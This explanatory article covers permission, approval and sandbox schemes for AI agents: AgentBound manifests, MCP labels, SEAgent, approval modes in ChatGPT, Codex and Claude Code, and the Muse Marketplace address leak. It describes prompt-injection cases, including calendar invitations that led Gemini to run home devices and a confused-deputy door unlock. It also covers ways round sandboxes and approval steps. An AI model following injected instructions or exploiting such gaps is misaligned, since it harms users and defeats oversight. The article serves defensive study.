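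AgentBound then runs the server in a container, an isolated environment that starts with no privileges and gains only the approved ones. If the agent requests a permission that the manifest doesn't cover, AgentBound stops the run.

| | Forecast server | Window-camera server |
|---|---|---|
| Declared capability | Outgoing network access | Camera |
| Permission after narrowing | The National Weather Service's address | The whole camera |
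| Can it read the user's documents? | No | No |
| Can it contact the weather blog? | No | No |
| Can the user limit it to one photo? | Not applicable | No |

No published test has included the design in the right-hand column. Bühler and colleagues implemented detailed limits for files, environment variables and the network. They explain that a container on a Unix-based system can be given access to a camera or microphone, but only on an "all-or-nothing" basis, and that Windows would need separate work. Finer control would require a trusted companion app that passes on each picture. Until someone builds one, a server with camera access can use the camera for as long as the server runs.

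The network limit is also looser than the one shown in the dialog. The user approves an exact web address, but the container looks up the host's IP address and lets the server connect to that. Like the Claude Code sandbox, the container can't separate the rain hub's readings from its broadcast.

The manifest for a camera server needn't declare camera access. A server that downloads pictures from a networked camera over the home network may declare only `mcp.ac.network.client`, so the user would have to notice from the address or the description that the server was for a camera.

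### What 296 popular servers needed

To find out which capabilities servers use, Bühler and colleagues took the 300 servers with the most GitHub stars from a directory of about 6,000. They could download and analyse 296. For each server, an OpenAI model drafted five manifests from the code and documentation, and a second model merged them into one.

| Capability | Share of the 296 servers |
|---|---|
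| Outgoing network access | 83.1% |
| Reading environment variables | 79.6% |
| Reading files | 74.1% |
| Writing files | 49.3% |

Few servers needed a camera, a microphone or another peripheral. The typical popular server connects an online service to the user's files and keys, so a single program often has access to both private data and a way to send it out, even before the user adds a second server.

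The sample probably understates device access in homes. GitHub stars come mainly from developers, who may be less interested in a server for a garden camera than in one for a database. The percentages also describe what a model inferred the code needed, so their usefulness depends on how accurate the manifests are.

Bühler and colleagues checked this in two ways. They first sent manifests to the developers of 96 servers. Of these, 71 didn't reply and four were still discussing the question. Of the remaining 21, 17 accepted the manifest and four rejected it, which gives the reported accuracy of 80.9%. If one more developer had rejected the manifest, that figure would have fallen by almost five percentage points, and developers who reply to such a request may differ from those who don't. The objections were still useful. One developer pointed out that a server needed only a few named environment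 variables, and another said that a server didn't read local files.

Two of the researchers also wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, 24 each, and compared them with the automatic ones. The two versions agreed on 787 of 816 decisions, or about 96%. Many of those decisions were easy, since few servers could plausibly need a speaker or a camera. The complete manifests matched for 28 of the 48 servers.

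In 23 of the 29 disagreements, the model missed a capability that the researchers had listed. The developers who replied hadn't reported any missing capabilities, but the lack of such reports is weak evidence that none were missing. Because AgentBound denies anything the manifest doesn't list, an omission is more likely to break a tool than to expose the user's data.

### When permission to run commands includes a phone's camera

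In their survey, Bühler and colleagues generated a second set of manifests using Android's list of permissions. A few servers now appeared to need access to the camera, precise location or text messages, under 2% for each permission.

The researchers inspected those servers and found that none used a sensor on the computer. The servers controlled an Android phone through the Android Debug Bridge, a developer tool that sends commands from a computer to a connected phone. The researchers therefore classed the Android permissions as false positives and concluded that the servers should declare `mcp.ac.system.exec`, the capability to run commands.

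That label correctly describes what the server does on the computer. But a user reading the manifest would see no mention of a camera or text messages, even though the agent might be able to access both through a phone plugged in to charge. The phone has to accept commands from that computer, which people who develop or test apps have often already allowed.

Permission to run commands can include access to any sensor that a command can reach. On a laptop, the operating system may still block the program that runs the command from using the built-in camera. It can't extend that block to a separate phone, which has its own permissions and may already trust the computer.

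Outgoing network access poses a smaller version of the same problem, because a server can use it to reach networked cameras. If a manifest doesn't list `mcp.ac.peripheral.camera`, the server can't access the computer's own camera directly. To rule out pictures altogether, someone has to check what the server's commands and network connections can reach.

A container helps with this if it doesn't give the server access to the connected phone or to the program that controls it. A server that operates the phone needs both, so the user has to decide how far to trust it with everything on the phone. A narrower tool, such as one that only reads the phone's battery level, would avoid that decision.

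### Which attacks AgentBound stopped

Bühler and colleagues first tested AgentBound on a malicious server they wrote to steal the private key that a developer uses to log in to other computers. Without AgentBound, the server read the key and sent it out. With only the network blocked, the server could read the key but not send it. With the full restrictions, it couldn't read the key either.

In a further test with 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections, AgentBound stopped eight and failed to stop five. The last server combined several attacks, and AgentBound stopped only those that needed files, commands or connections the policy didn't allow.

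| Server | What the attack tried to do | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Google Maps server | Replace Google's address with an attacker's | Stopped |
| Weather server | Replace the forecast service's address in the same way | Stopped |
| Tool with a changing description | Behave normally at first, then tell the agent to collect secret keys | Stopped |
| Clock server | Use its description to redirect payments made with another server's tool | Not stopped |
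| WeChat server | Insert extra commands into a database query | Not stopped |

The clock server shows the limit most clearly. It never contacted the payment service, but the model received its description along with those of the other tools. The description was meant to make the model change the payee in a payment that the second server had permission to make. At the container level, an allowed program contacted an allowed address.

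The same would be true of a door lock. If a forecast server's description leads the model to call `unlock_front_door`, the lock's server connects to the lock as usual, so AgentBound would allow the connection.

The tests also gave AgentBound favourable conditions. For ten of the 14 servers, the researchers wrote the manifests by hand during testing, and one tester approved the permissions. A user who doesn't suspect a server might approve a whole folder where the tester approved one file. None of the tests involved a camera, microphone or location service, so the results support AgentBound's limits on files and connections but provide little evidence about sensors.

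### Limiting which home devices an assistant can see

Home Assistant, a widely used open-source program for running a smart home, organises the home into entities, each of which is one reading or one controllable function. According to its documentation, the user chooses which entities to expose to its assistant. If the user connects a language model, the model gets only those entities and can't carry out administrative tasks. The same limit applies to outside agents that connect through Home Assistant's MCP server, introduced in February 2025.

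Under this arrangement, the user can expose the station's rain rate but not the indoor humidity, although both come from the same hub. This solves the problem from the first rain example, where one request returned both. The model also can't unlock the front door if Home Assistant hasn't exposed the lock to it.

An entity stays exposed until someone changes the setting, so if the user exposes the lock to let in a plumber, the assistant still has access to it afterward. Exposure covers both reading and operating an entity, so the user can't expose an ordinary lock just to let the assistant check that it is closed. The setting limits only requests that go through Home Assistant. An agent on the same network with an unrestricted fetch tool can still contact the rain hub directly.

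An agent without a device tool can also reach the device by messaging an agent that has one. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes a test in which one agent could search the web and another could operate a smart lock. The search agent came from a third party and had hidden instructions to open the door. It had no lock tool, so it broadcast a request to the other agents, and the lock agent unlocked the door. Security researchers call this a confused deputy attack, in which a program without authority gets a program with authority to act for it.

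In a second test, an owner asked the agent to let in their daughter, whose ID number was in a recent message. The defence under test, CaMeL, plans the sequence of tool calls before the agent reads any untrusted text, so a message can't add a call. But an attacker's text could still change the ID number, so the agent made the planned calls and gave access to the wrong person. A list of permitted devices wouldn't have helped, since the owner wanted the agent to use the lock.

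### Calendar invitations that operated home devices

In 2025, Ben Nassi, Stav Cohen and Or Yair demonstrated attacks of this kind on Google's Gemini assistants. Their paper, *Invitation Is All You Need!*, describes 14 scenarios targeting Gemini on the web, on phones and in Google Assistant.

The attacker needed only the target's email address to send a calendar invitation containing hidden instructions. When the target later asked Gemini about upcoming events, Gemini read the invitation along with the rest of the calendar. In some scenarios, the attacker instructed Gemini to wait for an ordinary reply, such as a word of thanks, before acting, so the harmful action appeared to follow from the target's reply.

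In a real home, the researchers got Gemini to switch off lights, open motorised shutters and turn on a boiler. In other scenarios, Gemini deleted calendar events or revealed the user's location. In another, it opened a link that started a Zoom call and streamed video of the user. Gemini didn't need camera permission, because Zoom already had it. As with the connected phone, the agent reached a sensor through a program it could start.

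The researchers rated 73% of the threats they analysed as high or critical risks to users. Each rating combines their estimates of likelihood and harm, so the 73% is not an attack success rate.

The researchers reported the attacks to Google in February 2025, and Google added defences before they published in August. Google now asks users to confirm more of the sensitive actions, checks web addresses more strictly and uses classifiers to look for planted instructions. The researchers estimated that these measures reduced the risks to between very low and medium. The confirmation step is the most relevant to a boiler because it works even if the classifier misses the instruction, as long as the user reads the request before accepting.

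Google Home gave Gemini legitimate access to all these devices, which the user had linked on purpose. As with the weather blog and the rain hub, the weakness was that Gemini could read a stranger's text and control the boiler in the same conversation.

### Labels for local, remote and physical effects

A host could look for such combinations automatically if every tool were labelled accurately. MCP has four behavioural labels. Besides `readOnlyHint` and `openWorldHint`, a server can declare whether a change is destructive and whether repeating a call has any further effect.

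These labels work poorly for sensors. A tool that photographs a bedroom changes nothing and contacts no outside party, so its developer could truthfully label it read-only and closed to the outside world, just like a calculator. The Model Context Protocol suggests that a host might skip confirmation for a read-only tool from a trusted server, which would be reasonable for the calculator but not for the bedroom camera.

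The meaning of "outside" also depends on the host. It might mean beyond the laptop for one server and beyond the company's network for another, so the rain hub could count as inside or outside. In March 2026, developers had five open proposals for new or related labels, including ones for secret data and unsafe output. No MCP host then showed the existing labels in its approval prompts or let users filter tools by them.

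GitLab, which makes software for programming teams, sorts its agents' tools into read, write and delete. In GitLab's *Agent tool governance*, an administrator can set each tool to run silently, ask the user first or stay blocked. The three categories are easy to understand and work for a code repository, where deletion is usually the worst outcome. They would work less well in a home, because viewing a bedroom camera would count as a read, the mildest category, despite the invasion of privacy.

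The labels that Ji and colleagues propose for their system, SEAgent, come closer to what a home needs. Each tool has five:

- what it acts on: something local, external or physical
- what it does: read, write or execute
- how serious the effect could be: low, moderate or high
- whether its results are trusted or unfiltered
- whether its results are general or personal

SEAgent records where information has travelled and checks that path against a set of rules. One rule blocks a call to a write or execute tool of moderate or high sensitivity if unfiltered text from an external tool led to the call. After the agent has read the weather blog, this rule would stop it from unlocking the front door. Unlike AgentBound, SEAgent can therefore block an otherwise allowed tool because of what the agent read earlier.

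SEAgent also tries to handle delayed instructions like the ones in the calendar invitations. It clears the agent's context after each exchange. If a later request needs something from an earlier exchange, SEAgent restores that item with the record of where it came from.

In published tests on AgentDojo, a collection of simulated office, banking and travel tasks, attacks succeeded in 39.14% of cases against an unprotected agent and in none against SEAgent. On another test, SEAgent reduced the success rate of attacks that could cause physical harm from 21.76% to zero. When the attack came from a poisoned document store that the agent searched, the success rate fell from 80% to zero. The main side effect was that SEAgent blocked two harmless tasks because the agent had consulted Wikipedia before recording health data or booking an appointment.

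All of this depends on the labels being right and the tools behaving as described. The researchers labelled the tools with a language model and corrected the results by hand, which a person installing an unknown MCP server can't be expected to do. SEAgent also allows any action that no rule forbids, whereas AgentBound blocks whatever the user hasn't approved.

The rules the researchers tested don't fully cover sensors. The rule against untrusted text applies to tools that write or execute, so it wouldn't stop the weather blog from making the agent take a photo if the camera tool is labelled as one that reads. A separate rule stops highly sensitive personal data from being sent by email, but not in the address of a web request. Users can add rules for both, but they would then have to accept more refusals of legitimate requests. The owner who wants to admit a daughter using the ID in a message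 already has this problem, because a rule against trusting messages would block the real ID as well as the attacker's.

| Scheme | Photograph of a bedroom | Unlocking the front door | What uses the label |
|---|---|---|---|
| MCP hints | Read-only, closed to the outside | Not read-only | The host, if its developer chooses |
| GitLab's categories, applied to a home | Read | Write | An administrator's rule: allow, ask or deny |
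| AgentBound | Camera, or network for a networked camera | Network or Bluetooth | The container |
| SEAgent | Read, personal | Physical, high sensitivity | Rules about where information has travelled |

None of these labels specifies which room a camera is in. *AC4A*, by Sharma and Grossman (2026), adds that kind of detail by defining each permission as an action on a particular resource. An application arranges its resources as a tree, such as year, month and day for a calendar, and the user grants permission to read or change one branch. When the agent makes a call, the application determines which resources the call needs, and AC4A allows it only if the user's permissions cover all of them.

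A home could use the same structure for rooms and devices. The user might let the agent read the garden camera and operate the kitchen lights, but block it from using the bedroom camera. Sharma and Grossman demonstrated AC4A on a game and a flight booking, so nobody has yet shown how well it would work with household equipment. AC4A also relies on the application to match each call to the right resource. If someone moves the garden camera into the bedroom without renaming it, AC4A will still let the agent take pictures there.

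## Who approves an agent's request for access

A permission can specify a device, such as a garden camera, without specifying who decides whether the agent may use it. The harness can ask the user before each call, apply a rule the user set earlier, have a second model review the call, or predict what the user would choose. Many products combine these methods.

Suppose the user asks whether it is raining at the house, and the agent requests three calls: a web search for a forecast, a location reading to find the right town, and a photo through the window. The operating system's permissions apply to the whole app, so the harness has to approve or deny each call.

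### Asking the user each time

The harness pauses and shows the user the agent's request. According to OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*, an approval card in ChatGPT describes the connected app and the proposed action, and the user can refuse the action or allow it once.

A user can consider facts that the harness has no record of. An approval prompt for a photo might show only the tool's name, `take_window_photo`, but the user may know that someone is asleep on the sofa under the window. For a web search, the user needs to see the query, because a prompt that showed only "Search the web?" would not reveal a door code in the query.

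If the user allows a call by mistake, the permission covers only that call, so there is no stored grant to revoke. However, the user can't get back a picture that has already gone to the model's provider.

The main drawback is the number of prompts, which in this example is three for one weather question. According to Techlicious, Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts and calls the result "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention. The figure doesn't prove inattention, because most of the requests may have been reasonable. But users who refuse only about one request in 14 have usually approved many harmless ones before a harmful one arrives. A sandbox can reduce the number of prompts by making some actions safe enough to run without approval.

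### Applying a stored rule

With a stored rule, the user or an administrator decides in advance, and ordinary software compares each call with the rule. For example, the user might allow web searches and location readings but block the camera.

In Meta's Muse, a separate system called Sentinel first checks for a stored policy that authorises the agent's action and asks the user only if it finds none, according to SiliconANGLE. The user can limit a permission to one task, service, transaction or period, according to Axios' *Meta debuts Muse, its long-planned personal AI agent* (2026).

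A planted instruction can't override a fixed rule, but the software checks only what the rule specifies, usually the tool's name and sometimes its arguments. If a rule allows `take_window_photo`, the call goes ahead whether the user's question or an instruction on a stranger's weather blog prompted it.

Broad permission categories can let an agent use sensors without approval, because taking a photo may count as a read action. ChatGPT's "Allow read actions" setting, for example, lets it read from connected apps without asking. According to OpenAI documentation published by March 2026, Codex always asks before it calls a tool whose own metadata labels it destructive, even if the tool is also labeled read-only. That rule wouldn't cover a camera tool, since taking a photo isn't destructive.

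A mistake in a rule repeats until someone notices it, and changing the rule may not end the access. OpenAI warns that changing an app's permission in ChatGPT doesn't disconnect the app, so the user has to disconnect the account separately. In Claude Code, a rule that blocks a tool applies in every mode, including the one that skips permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, so blocking the camera tool there is more dependable than relying on a prompt.

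### Having a second model review the request

A reviewing model can consider what a call is for. It might approve a search for "rain in Leeds" and refuse the same search with a door code added. The camera call is harder, because the model has to judge whether someone who asks about rain has also agreed to a photo of the room. Reasonable people would disagree about that, and the same model might give different answers to the same request.

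The developer decides what information the reviewer gets. Chrome withholds raw page content from the model that checks its agent's actions, which makes the model harder to hijack but leaves it with less context. Michael and Roesner note that attackers who adapt their methods can get past such models.

If the reviewer wrongly approves a call, the user may never learn that there was a decision to make. The user can switch the reviewer off but may have no individual grant to withdraw, because the model judges each call separately.

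According to OpenClaw's *Permission modes*, its `auto` mode runs commands that match an allowlist and sends the rest to a reviewing model. The model asks a person only when it can't safely approve a command itself.

### Predicting the user's choice

A reviewing model judges whether a call is acceptable, whereas a prediction model estimates whether this particular user would allow it. The estimate can draw on the user's earlier decisions and those of people who made similar choices. If the user has allowed weather tools to read the location several times, the model will probably predict that the user would allow it again.

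When the prediction is wrong, the agent acts on consent the user never gave. Revoking that consent means correcting the model as well as stopping the call, or the agent may repeat the mistake in a slightly different situation. Michael and Roesner found two proposed systems that learned from users' choices but gave users no way to prevent or reverse this learning.

The four methods could treat the three calls like this:

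| Method | Web search for a forecast | Location reading | Picture through the window |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ask the user | The user checks the query for anything private | The user allows it or types the town's name instead | The user can check who is in view first |
| Stored rule | Runs if the rule allows searches, whatever the query contains | Runs if the rule allows location, even when a town's name would do | Gets the same answer whoever is in the room |
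| Second model | The model can refuse a query that contains a door code | The model judges whether the task needs it | The model judges whether the question implies consent |
| Prediction | Probably runs if the user has allowed searches before | Depends on the user's earlier answers | Relies on other people's answers if the user has never had such a request |

### What 21 proposals and five products offered

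Michael and Roesner began with 30 works on agent security and kept the 21 that described a concrete permission system for individual users. Eight were peer-reviewed papers, 12 were preprints and one was an open-source program.

Twelve of the systems reduced the user's work, for example by accepting rules in ordinary language or predicting them from the user's request. Eleven based their rules on formal methods, which give each rule a precise meaning. Twelve left enforcement to fixed code or the user instead of a model. No system did all three. Only six clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later, and two of those allowed changes only between sessions.

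The researchers then tested five commercial agents in late May and early June 2026: the Claude chatbot, Claude Cowork (Anthropic's desktop agent for office work), ChatGPT's chat mode, its agent mode, and Codex. They connected the chatbots to a Gmail account made for the study and gave the desktop agents a local folder. For each permission, they repeated the tasks under every available setting and then tried to revoke the permission. They didn't test access to a camera, microphone or location service.

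ChatGPT's agent mode operated a remote browser, and the researchers found no way to define what it could do there or to approve or deny individual actions. It used Gmail without approval, although chat mode required approval for the same actions. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* says that the agent paused when a site required a login and had the user take over the browser. The user could therefore keep the agent out of Gmail, but had no setting to let it read messages without also letting it send them.

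The Claude chatbot offered three settings for each permission: "Always allow", "Needs approval" and "Blocked". With "Needs approval" selected, Claude created an email draft without asking. The browser's log showed the call marked `approvalRequired: false`. When Michael and Roesner asked why, Claude replied that it had inferred permission from their request. A model's explanation of its own behavior is weak evidence of how the product works, but the log does show that Claude skipped the approval. Michael and Roesner concluded that a model sometimes reviewed actions under this setting without telling the user. Users could turn this off only by blocking the tool.

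An unsent draft does little harm. The same behaviour with a camera tool would be more serious, because the user would have chosen "Needs approval" to see the request before the camera took a picture.

In Claude Cowork, the researchers could grant access to a folder but couldn't revoke it. A new session started without the permission, but the old session stayed in the app's history and, if reopened, still had access to the folder. As far as they could determine, only the operating system's controls or uninstalling the app would end the access permanently.

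Michael and Roesner acknowledge that they couldn't inspect the code of these products, that the products change quickly, and that agents can behave differently from one run to the next. They repeated the surprising results in new sessions. They reproduced Claude's self-approval at least three times in June and July and reported it to Anthropic on July 2.

### What has changed since the survey

OpenAI has retired ChatGPT's agent mode. Quick Online Tips' *How to Use ChatGPT Agent (Now ChatGPT Work)* (2026) quotes an OpenAI help page that directs users to ChatGPT Work, which the company introduced on July 9. Unlike agent mode, ChatGPT Work has a setting for approving the websites its cloud browser uses. MacStories reported in August that it asks the user before using a website by default. The user can instead let ChatGPT approve sites after checking their relevance and risk, or always allow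 them, which OpenAI discourages. The user can also allow or block individual sites, but allowing a webmail site doesn't specify which messages the agent should read there.

ChatGPT's chat mode has changed too. Michael and Roesner found that it required approval for every action and had no way to give approval in advance. By the end of August, OpenAI's help page listed four settings for connected apps:

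- **Always ask** requires approval for reading as well as for changes.
- **Allow read actions** requires approval only for changes.
- **Allow low-risk actions** approves those automatically, while riskier ones may need confirmation or fail.
- **Allow all actions** removes the additional prompts, and OpenAI warns that it carries elevated risk.

A user can't make the most permissive setting the default for the whole account, but may be able to choose it for one app. A user with two email accounts can also set a different permission for each.

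It is less clear whether Anthropic has changed the two behaviours that the survey found in Claude. As of August 30, Anthropic's *Claude for Chrome permissions guide* describes a "Manually approve" mode, previously called "Ask before acting", in which Claude pauses before each action. But the guide covers the browser extension, so it doesn't show whether the chatbot still approves its own drafts or whether Cowork users can now revoke access to a folder. Anyone who relies on either control can test it with an unimportant draft or an empty folder.

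### Permission modes in ChatGPT's desktop app and Codex

OpenAI merged the Codex desktop app into the ChatGPT desktop app from July 9, according to PPC Land's *OpenAI kills Atlas browser, folds it into new ChatGPT Work agent*. Codex also runs in the command line and in code editors. As of September 3, OpenAI's *权限*, the Chinese edition of its permissions guide, describes modes that apply to all of these.

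| Mode | What the agent can do without asking the user | Who decides on further access |
|---|---|---|
| Ask for approval | Read and edit files in its workspace and run routine commands | The user |
| Auto-review | The same | A reviewing model |
| Full access | Edit any file on the computer and run commands that use the network | Nobody, because the agent doesn't have to ask |

The workspace is the folder the agent is working in. In "Ask for approval", the agent also asks before using the internet. This mode is always available. The other two appear in the desktop app's permissions menu only after the user enables them in the settings. Enabling a mode doesn't select it or change existing chats. An organisation can also make some modes unavailable.

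Each mode combines a sandbox with an approval setting. Switching from "Ask for approval" to "Auto-review" lets a model decide on requests instead of the user, but doesn't change the sandbox. "Full access" removes both the sandbox restrictions and the approval step.

Michael and Roesner credited Codex with making its reviewing model explicit, since it was off by default and the user could turn it off at any time. But the reviewing model applied to every tool in the session, so a user who wanted it to approve file edits couldn't reserve decisions about email for themselves.

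These modes cover files, commands and the internet, but have no separate settings for the camera or location. Web search has its own control, so a developer can let Codex search while the commands it runs stay offline. "Full access" in ChatGPT, which is different from Full Disk Access on a Mac, removes OpenAI's restrictions. macOS should still block the agent from taking a picture if the app doesn't have camera permission. If the app already has that permission, the agent may be able to take a picture without asking the user again.

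### How well software predicted people's choices

In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) tested whether a model could learn a person's preferences well enough to decide for them. They recruited 205 US adults through Prolific, a site for paid research participants, and removed two for invalid responses.

The participants used a website that asked them to train an imaginary personal assistant. They answered five questions about which tools and data the assistant needed, then 20 about whether it could share particular data to complete a request. Each time, they could choose to always share the data, share it but be asked again, refuse but be asked again, or never share it. In five of the 20 permission questions, the assistant requested some data that the task didn't need.

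The participants responded to written scenarios, so they decided based on descriptions of a weather lookup or fitness record, not live sensor readings. None of the 21 tools in the scenarios was a camera or microphone.

Participants overshared more often than they undershared. At least once, 97.0% shared unnecessary data and 91.1% withheld data that the task required. Nobody gave the appropriate answer every time. Some of the refusals were probably deliberate, since participants withheld a child's name 65.1% of the time and passport information 54.0% of the time.

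Participants shared unnecessary data about 78% of the time when they mistakenly thought the assistant needed it, and still shared it in more than a third of cases when they correctly saw that it didn't. A prompt that explained why the agent requested a location might therefore prevent some over-sharing, but only if the explanation were true.

Preferences also differed by subject:

| Subject | "Always share" | "Never share" |
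|---|---|---|
| Entertainment | 55.6% | 2.9% |
| Health and fitness | 48.9% | 7.7% |
| Smart home | 41.6% | 9.3% |
| Travel | 36.0% | 10.5% |
| Finance | 22.2% | 16.9% |

Participants chose "always share" for the weather tool 50.8% of the time. The study's only dedicated smart-home tool controlled lights, so the smart-home figure is weak evidence of how people would treat a bedroom camera.

Wu and colleagues predicted the decisions by giving an OpenAI model each person's earlier answers, age group and attitudes to privacy. A second system looked for participants with similar preferences and supplied its most confident recommendations. The combined system was right 85.1% of the time. It would have shared 15.2% of the data that participants had refused to share, and withheld 14.8% of the data they had agreed to share.

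Accuracy rose to 94.4% (about one decision in 18 was wrong) when the system decided just the requests it was most confident about. But those made up only 25.9% of requests, so the user would have to decide the rest.

The test by Wu and colleagues counted only "always" and "never" answers, which left out the hardest cases, the decisions that participants wanted to reconsider next time. Participants agreed to share in 69.3% of the remaining cases, so a program that approved every request would have been 69.3% accurate. Without a user's earlier answers, the prediction system was only 66.9% accurate, though it would have made far fewer unwanted disclosures than that program. With answers from one to four earlier requests, its accuracy rose to 77.7%.

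Accuracy also varied from person to person. The system predicted every decision correctly for 12.7% of users, but only 49.0% of decisions for one user whose preferences differed greatly across subjects. Of all the subjects, it was least accurate on smart-home requests, at 80.1%, mostly because it refused too often.

Wu and colleagues present the system as a proof of concept and expect users to keep making the uncertain decisions. For the rain question, the system might reasonably learn that a user doesn't mind weather searches, but nothing in the study supports letting it decide when to turn on a camera.

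### The Muse Marketplace case

In September 2026, Matt Robb, a technology reviewer in Toronto, let Muse handle his listing for a keyboard on Facebook Marketplace. Bot Mutiny's *Meta's Muse AI Agent Shared a Seller's Home Address* (2026) relays the Guardian's account of what followed. A buyer named Usman asked whether the keyboard was still available. Muse agreed on a price and sent him Robb's home address. When Usman arrived with his wife and daughter and sent a message, Muse replied "yep I'm here!" Robb wasn't there and didn't know about the sale. Usman waited 20 minutes before giving up.

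Robb said he had entered the address as the pickup location but had never allowed Muse to give it to buyers. Meta later told him that Muse had shared it because of "always allow" permissions he had granted when he connected Muse to his Marketplace profile, KSL reports. The address was part of a template for replying to buyers. Robb had expected Muse to check with him before it shared the address or accepted an offer.

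Meta's reading of the permission can be defended, because sellers normally tell a buyer where to collect an item, and a pickup address in a reply template has little other use. A stored rule covering replies to buyers would have allowed the message, and a reviewing model might have classified it as an ordinary part of a sale.

But Robb's permission didn't settle who would get the address or when. Consent to a data source allows the agent to read or use certain information, while consent to a disclosure allows it to send specific information to a specific recipient for a specific purpose. Robb had given the first kind when he connected his profile, and he understood that the second would require asking him again. A prompt such as "Send your home address to Usman, who wants to collect the keyboard tonight?" would have let him decide, and he would also have learned from it that he needed to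 be at home.

Similarly, in the rain example, a user who lets the agent read the laptop's location to find a forecast hasn't necessarily agreed to let it send that location to a weather blog. If the harness stores only "location: allowed", it can't distinguish permission to read the location from permission to send it. It would need a separate rule for sending the location that names the recipient.

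Asking before every such message would again give users too many prompts. Meta's executives told Axios that they were aware of this problem, and that Muse requires approval for more sensitive actions but lets authorised, lower-risk tasks proceed. Robb's case suggests that an agent should need approval before first giving a home address to a stranger, even when the seller has authorised routine replies.

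Robb later disconnected Muse from most of his apps. That limited what the agent could do next, but Usman already had the address.

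## How sandboxes confine a running agent

Every method of approval sometimes lets a harmful action through. A sandbox still restricts what that action can do, because the operating system enforces the sandbox's limits regardless of who approved the action.

Claude Code is a useful example because Anthropic has documented its sandbox in detail and published the code behind it. The sandbox works on macOS, Linux and WSL2 (a Linux environment inside Windows), but not for commands run directly on Windows. It is off by default. If a required component is missing on Linux, Claude Code normally runs commands without the sandbox, but the `failIfUnavailable` setting makes it exit instead.

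### Limits on files, network, processes and devices

A program can open files, connect to other computers, start or control other programs, and use hardware. A sandbox has to limit each of these separately, and Claude Code does this with different parts of the operating system.

| Limit | Linux | macOS |
|---|---|---|
| Files | bubblewrap makes most folders read-only for the command | Seatbelt refuses changes outside the permitted folders |
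| Network | The command gets a separate network with no outside connection | Seatbelt blocks connections except the one to Claude Code's proxy |
| Processes | Programs the command starts stay inside; an optional filter blocks messages to programs outside | Programs the command starts stay inside; Seatbelt blocks instructions to other apps |
| Devices | Not described in Anthropic's guides | Not described, though macOS has its own camera and microphone permissions |

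Bubblewrap is a small program that starts another program with a restricted view of the computer. If the restricted program tries to change a read-only file, the kernel, the core of the operating system, returns an error. Seatbelt is built into macOS and checks a program's attempted actions against a list of rules.

By default, a command can write only to the project folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added. It can read almost everything on the computer. It can't contact any website until someone allows it.

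The process limit blocks two ways of getting around the other limits. A command might start a second program to do what it can't do itself, so the sandbox applies the same restrictions to that program. A command might also use a program that is already running outside the sandbox. On a Mac, apps can control each other through messages called Apple Events, which the sandbox blocks by default. If the user allows these messages, a command can launch other apps outside the sandbox without a prompt.

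Linux programs often send each other messages through Unix sockets. Blocking these sockets requires a filter the user has to install separately. A command that can reach a socket may be able to do whatever the program listening on it can do, and Anthropic warns that access to Docker's socket effectively gives a command access to the whole computer.

### One download, one refused write and one refused connection

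Suppose the user keeps a rain diary in a folder called `rain-diary`, turns on the sandbox and asks Claude Code to add last month's official rainfall.

1. Claude requests a command that downloads a file from the National Weather Service. In the sandbox's auto-allow mode, Claude Code starts the command without asking.
2. The command has no direct route to the internet. Claude Code has given it settings that tell it to send web requests to a proxy, which runs on the same laptop but outside the sandbox.
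3. The proxy compares the site's name with a list of allowed domains. The list starts empty, so Claude Code asks the user, who chooses "Yes". This allows the site for the rest of the session.
4. The proxy looks up the site's IP address. It would refuse if the name led only to the laptop itself or to a link-local address, but this one leads to a public server, so the proxy connects.
5. The command saves the file in `rain-diary`. The operating system permits this because the project folder is writable.

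The fourth step is less strict than the address check described earlier for fetch tools. If the user allows a name that leads to a private address, such as an office server at 10.4.0.15, the proxy connects to it. This is convenient for a company's developers, but allowing a name for the rain hub would also let the agent reach the hub. Before version 2.1.284, the proxy connected to any address an allowed name led to, including the laptop's own.

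Claude then tries to save a copy of the diary in the user's Documents folder, which isn't writable. The operating system blocks the write, and on Linux the command may report "Read-only file system". After the error, Claude can request to run the same command outside the sandbox. In Claude Code's manual mode, the user sees a prompt titled "Bash command (unsandboxed)". But if an older rule allows the command, Anthropic says the retry runs with no prompt. A user who wrote that rule to avoid interruptions may not have meant it to lift the sandbox. Strict sandbox mode turns off these retries.

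Suppose a script for drawing charts also tries to send the diary to the weather blog. If the script uses the proxy, Claude Code asks the user whether to allow a connection to `weatherblog.example`, and the connection fails if the user refuses. If the script tries to connect directly, the attempt fails because the script has no network access of its own. On Linux, it may report "Network is unreachable".

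The sandbox gives less protection when a user has turned off permission prompts. In Claude Code's `bypassPermissions` mode, the proxy allows sites that aren't on the allowlist, and the agent can retry commands outside the sandbox without a prompt. Anyone who leaves the agent running unattended with only the command sandbox on could easily miss these gaps. The `strictAllowlist` setting makes the proxy refuse unlisted sites in every mode.

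Some legitimate programs, including many database tools, also ignore the proxy, and they fail even when the user has allowed the site. The user can exempt such a program from the sandbox, but it then runs with the user's full access. If an exempted program runs a script in the project folder, Claude can edit the script and then run it outside the sandbox.

### Why file and network limits need each other

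Many developers keep a private key in a folder called `.ssh`, which lets them log in to other computers without a password. An older edition of Anthropic's sandbox guide lists this folder among those commands can read by default. With the default settings, the network limit is what keeps a malicious script from stealing the key.

| | Network limited to approved sites | Network open |
|---|---|---|
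| Key readable | The script can read the key but can't send it to an unapproved site | The script can read the key and send it anywhere |
| Key blocked | The script can neither read nor send the key | The script can't send this key but can send any other file it can read |

AgentBound's test with a key-stealing server, described earlier, covered three of these four cases, and the results were the same.

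The network limit also depends on the file limit, because a command that can write anywhere can weaken the network limit. Claude Code lets users switch off the file limit and keep the network limit. Anthropic warns that a command could then alter Claude Code's settings or the files a terminal loads at startup to get more access on the next run.

The sandbox protects parts of the project folder even though the rest is writable. A command can't change Claude Code's settings there or add an MCP server, because Claude Code would later start that server outside the sandbox. The user can't exempt one of these files without turning off the sandbox's file restrictions entirely.

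Sometimes an agent needs to use a credential without reading it. Claude Code can give a command a placeholder in place of a credential such as the user's GitHub token. When the command sends a request to an approved site, the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token. A malicious script that copies the placeholder gets nothing useful. The proxy has to decrypt the command's web traffic to make the replacement, which requires an experimental setting. On a Mac, Claude Code can replace tokens stored in environment variables this way, but if a token is stored in a file, it blocks access to the file instead.

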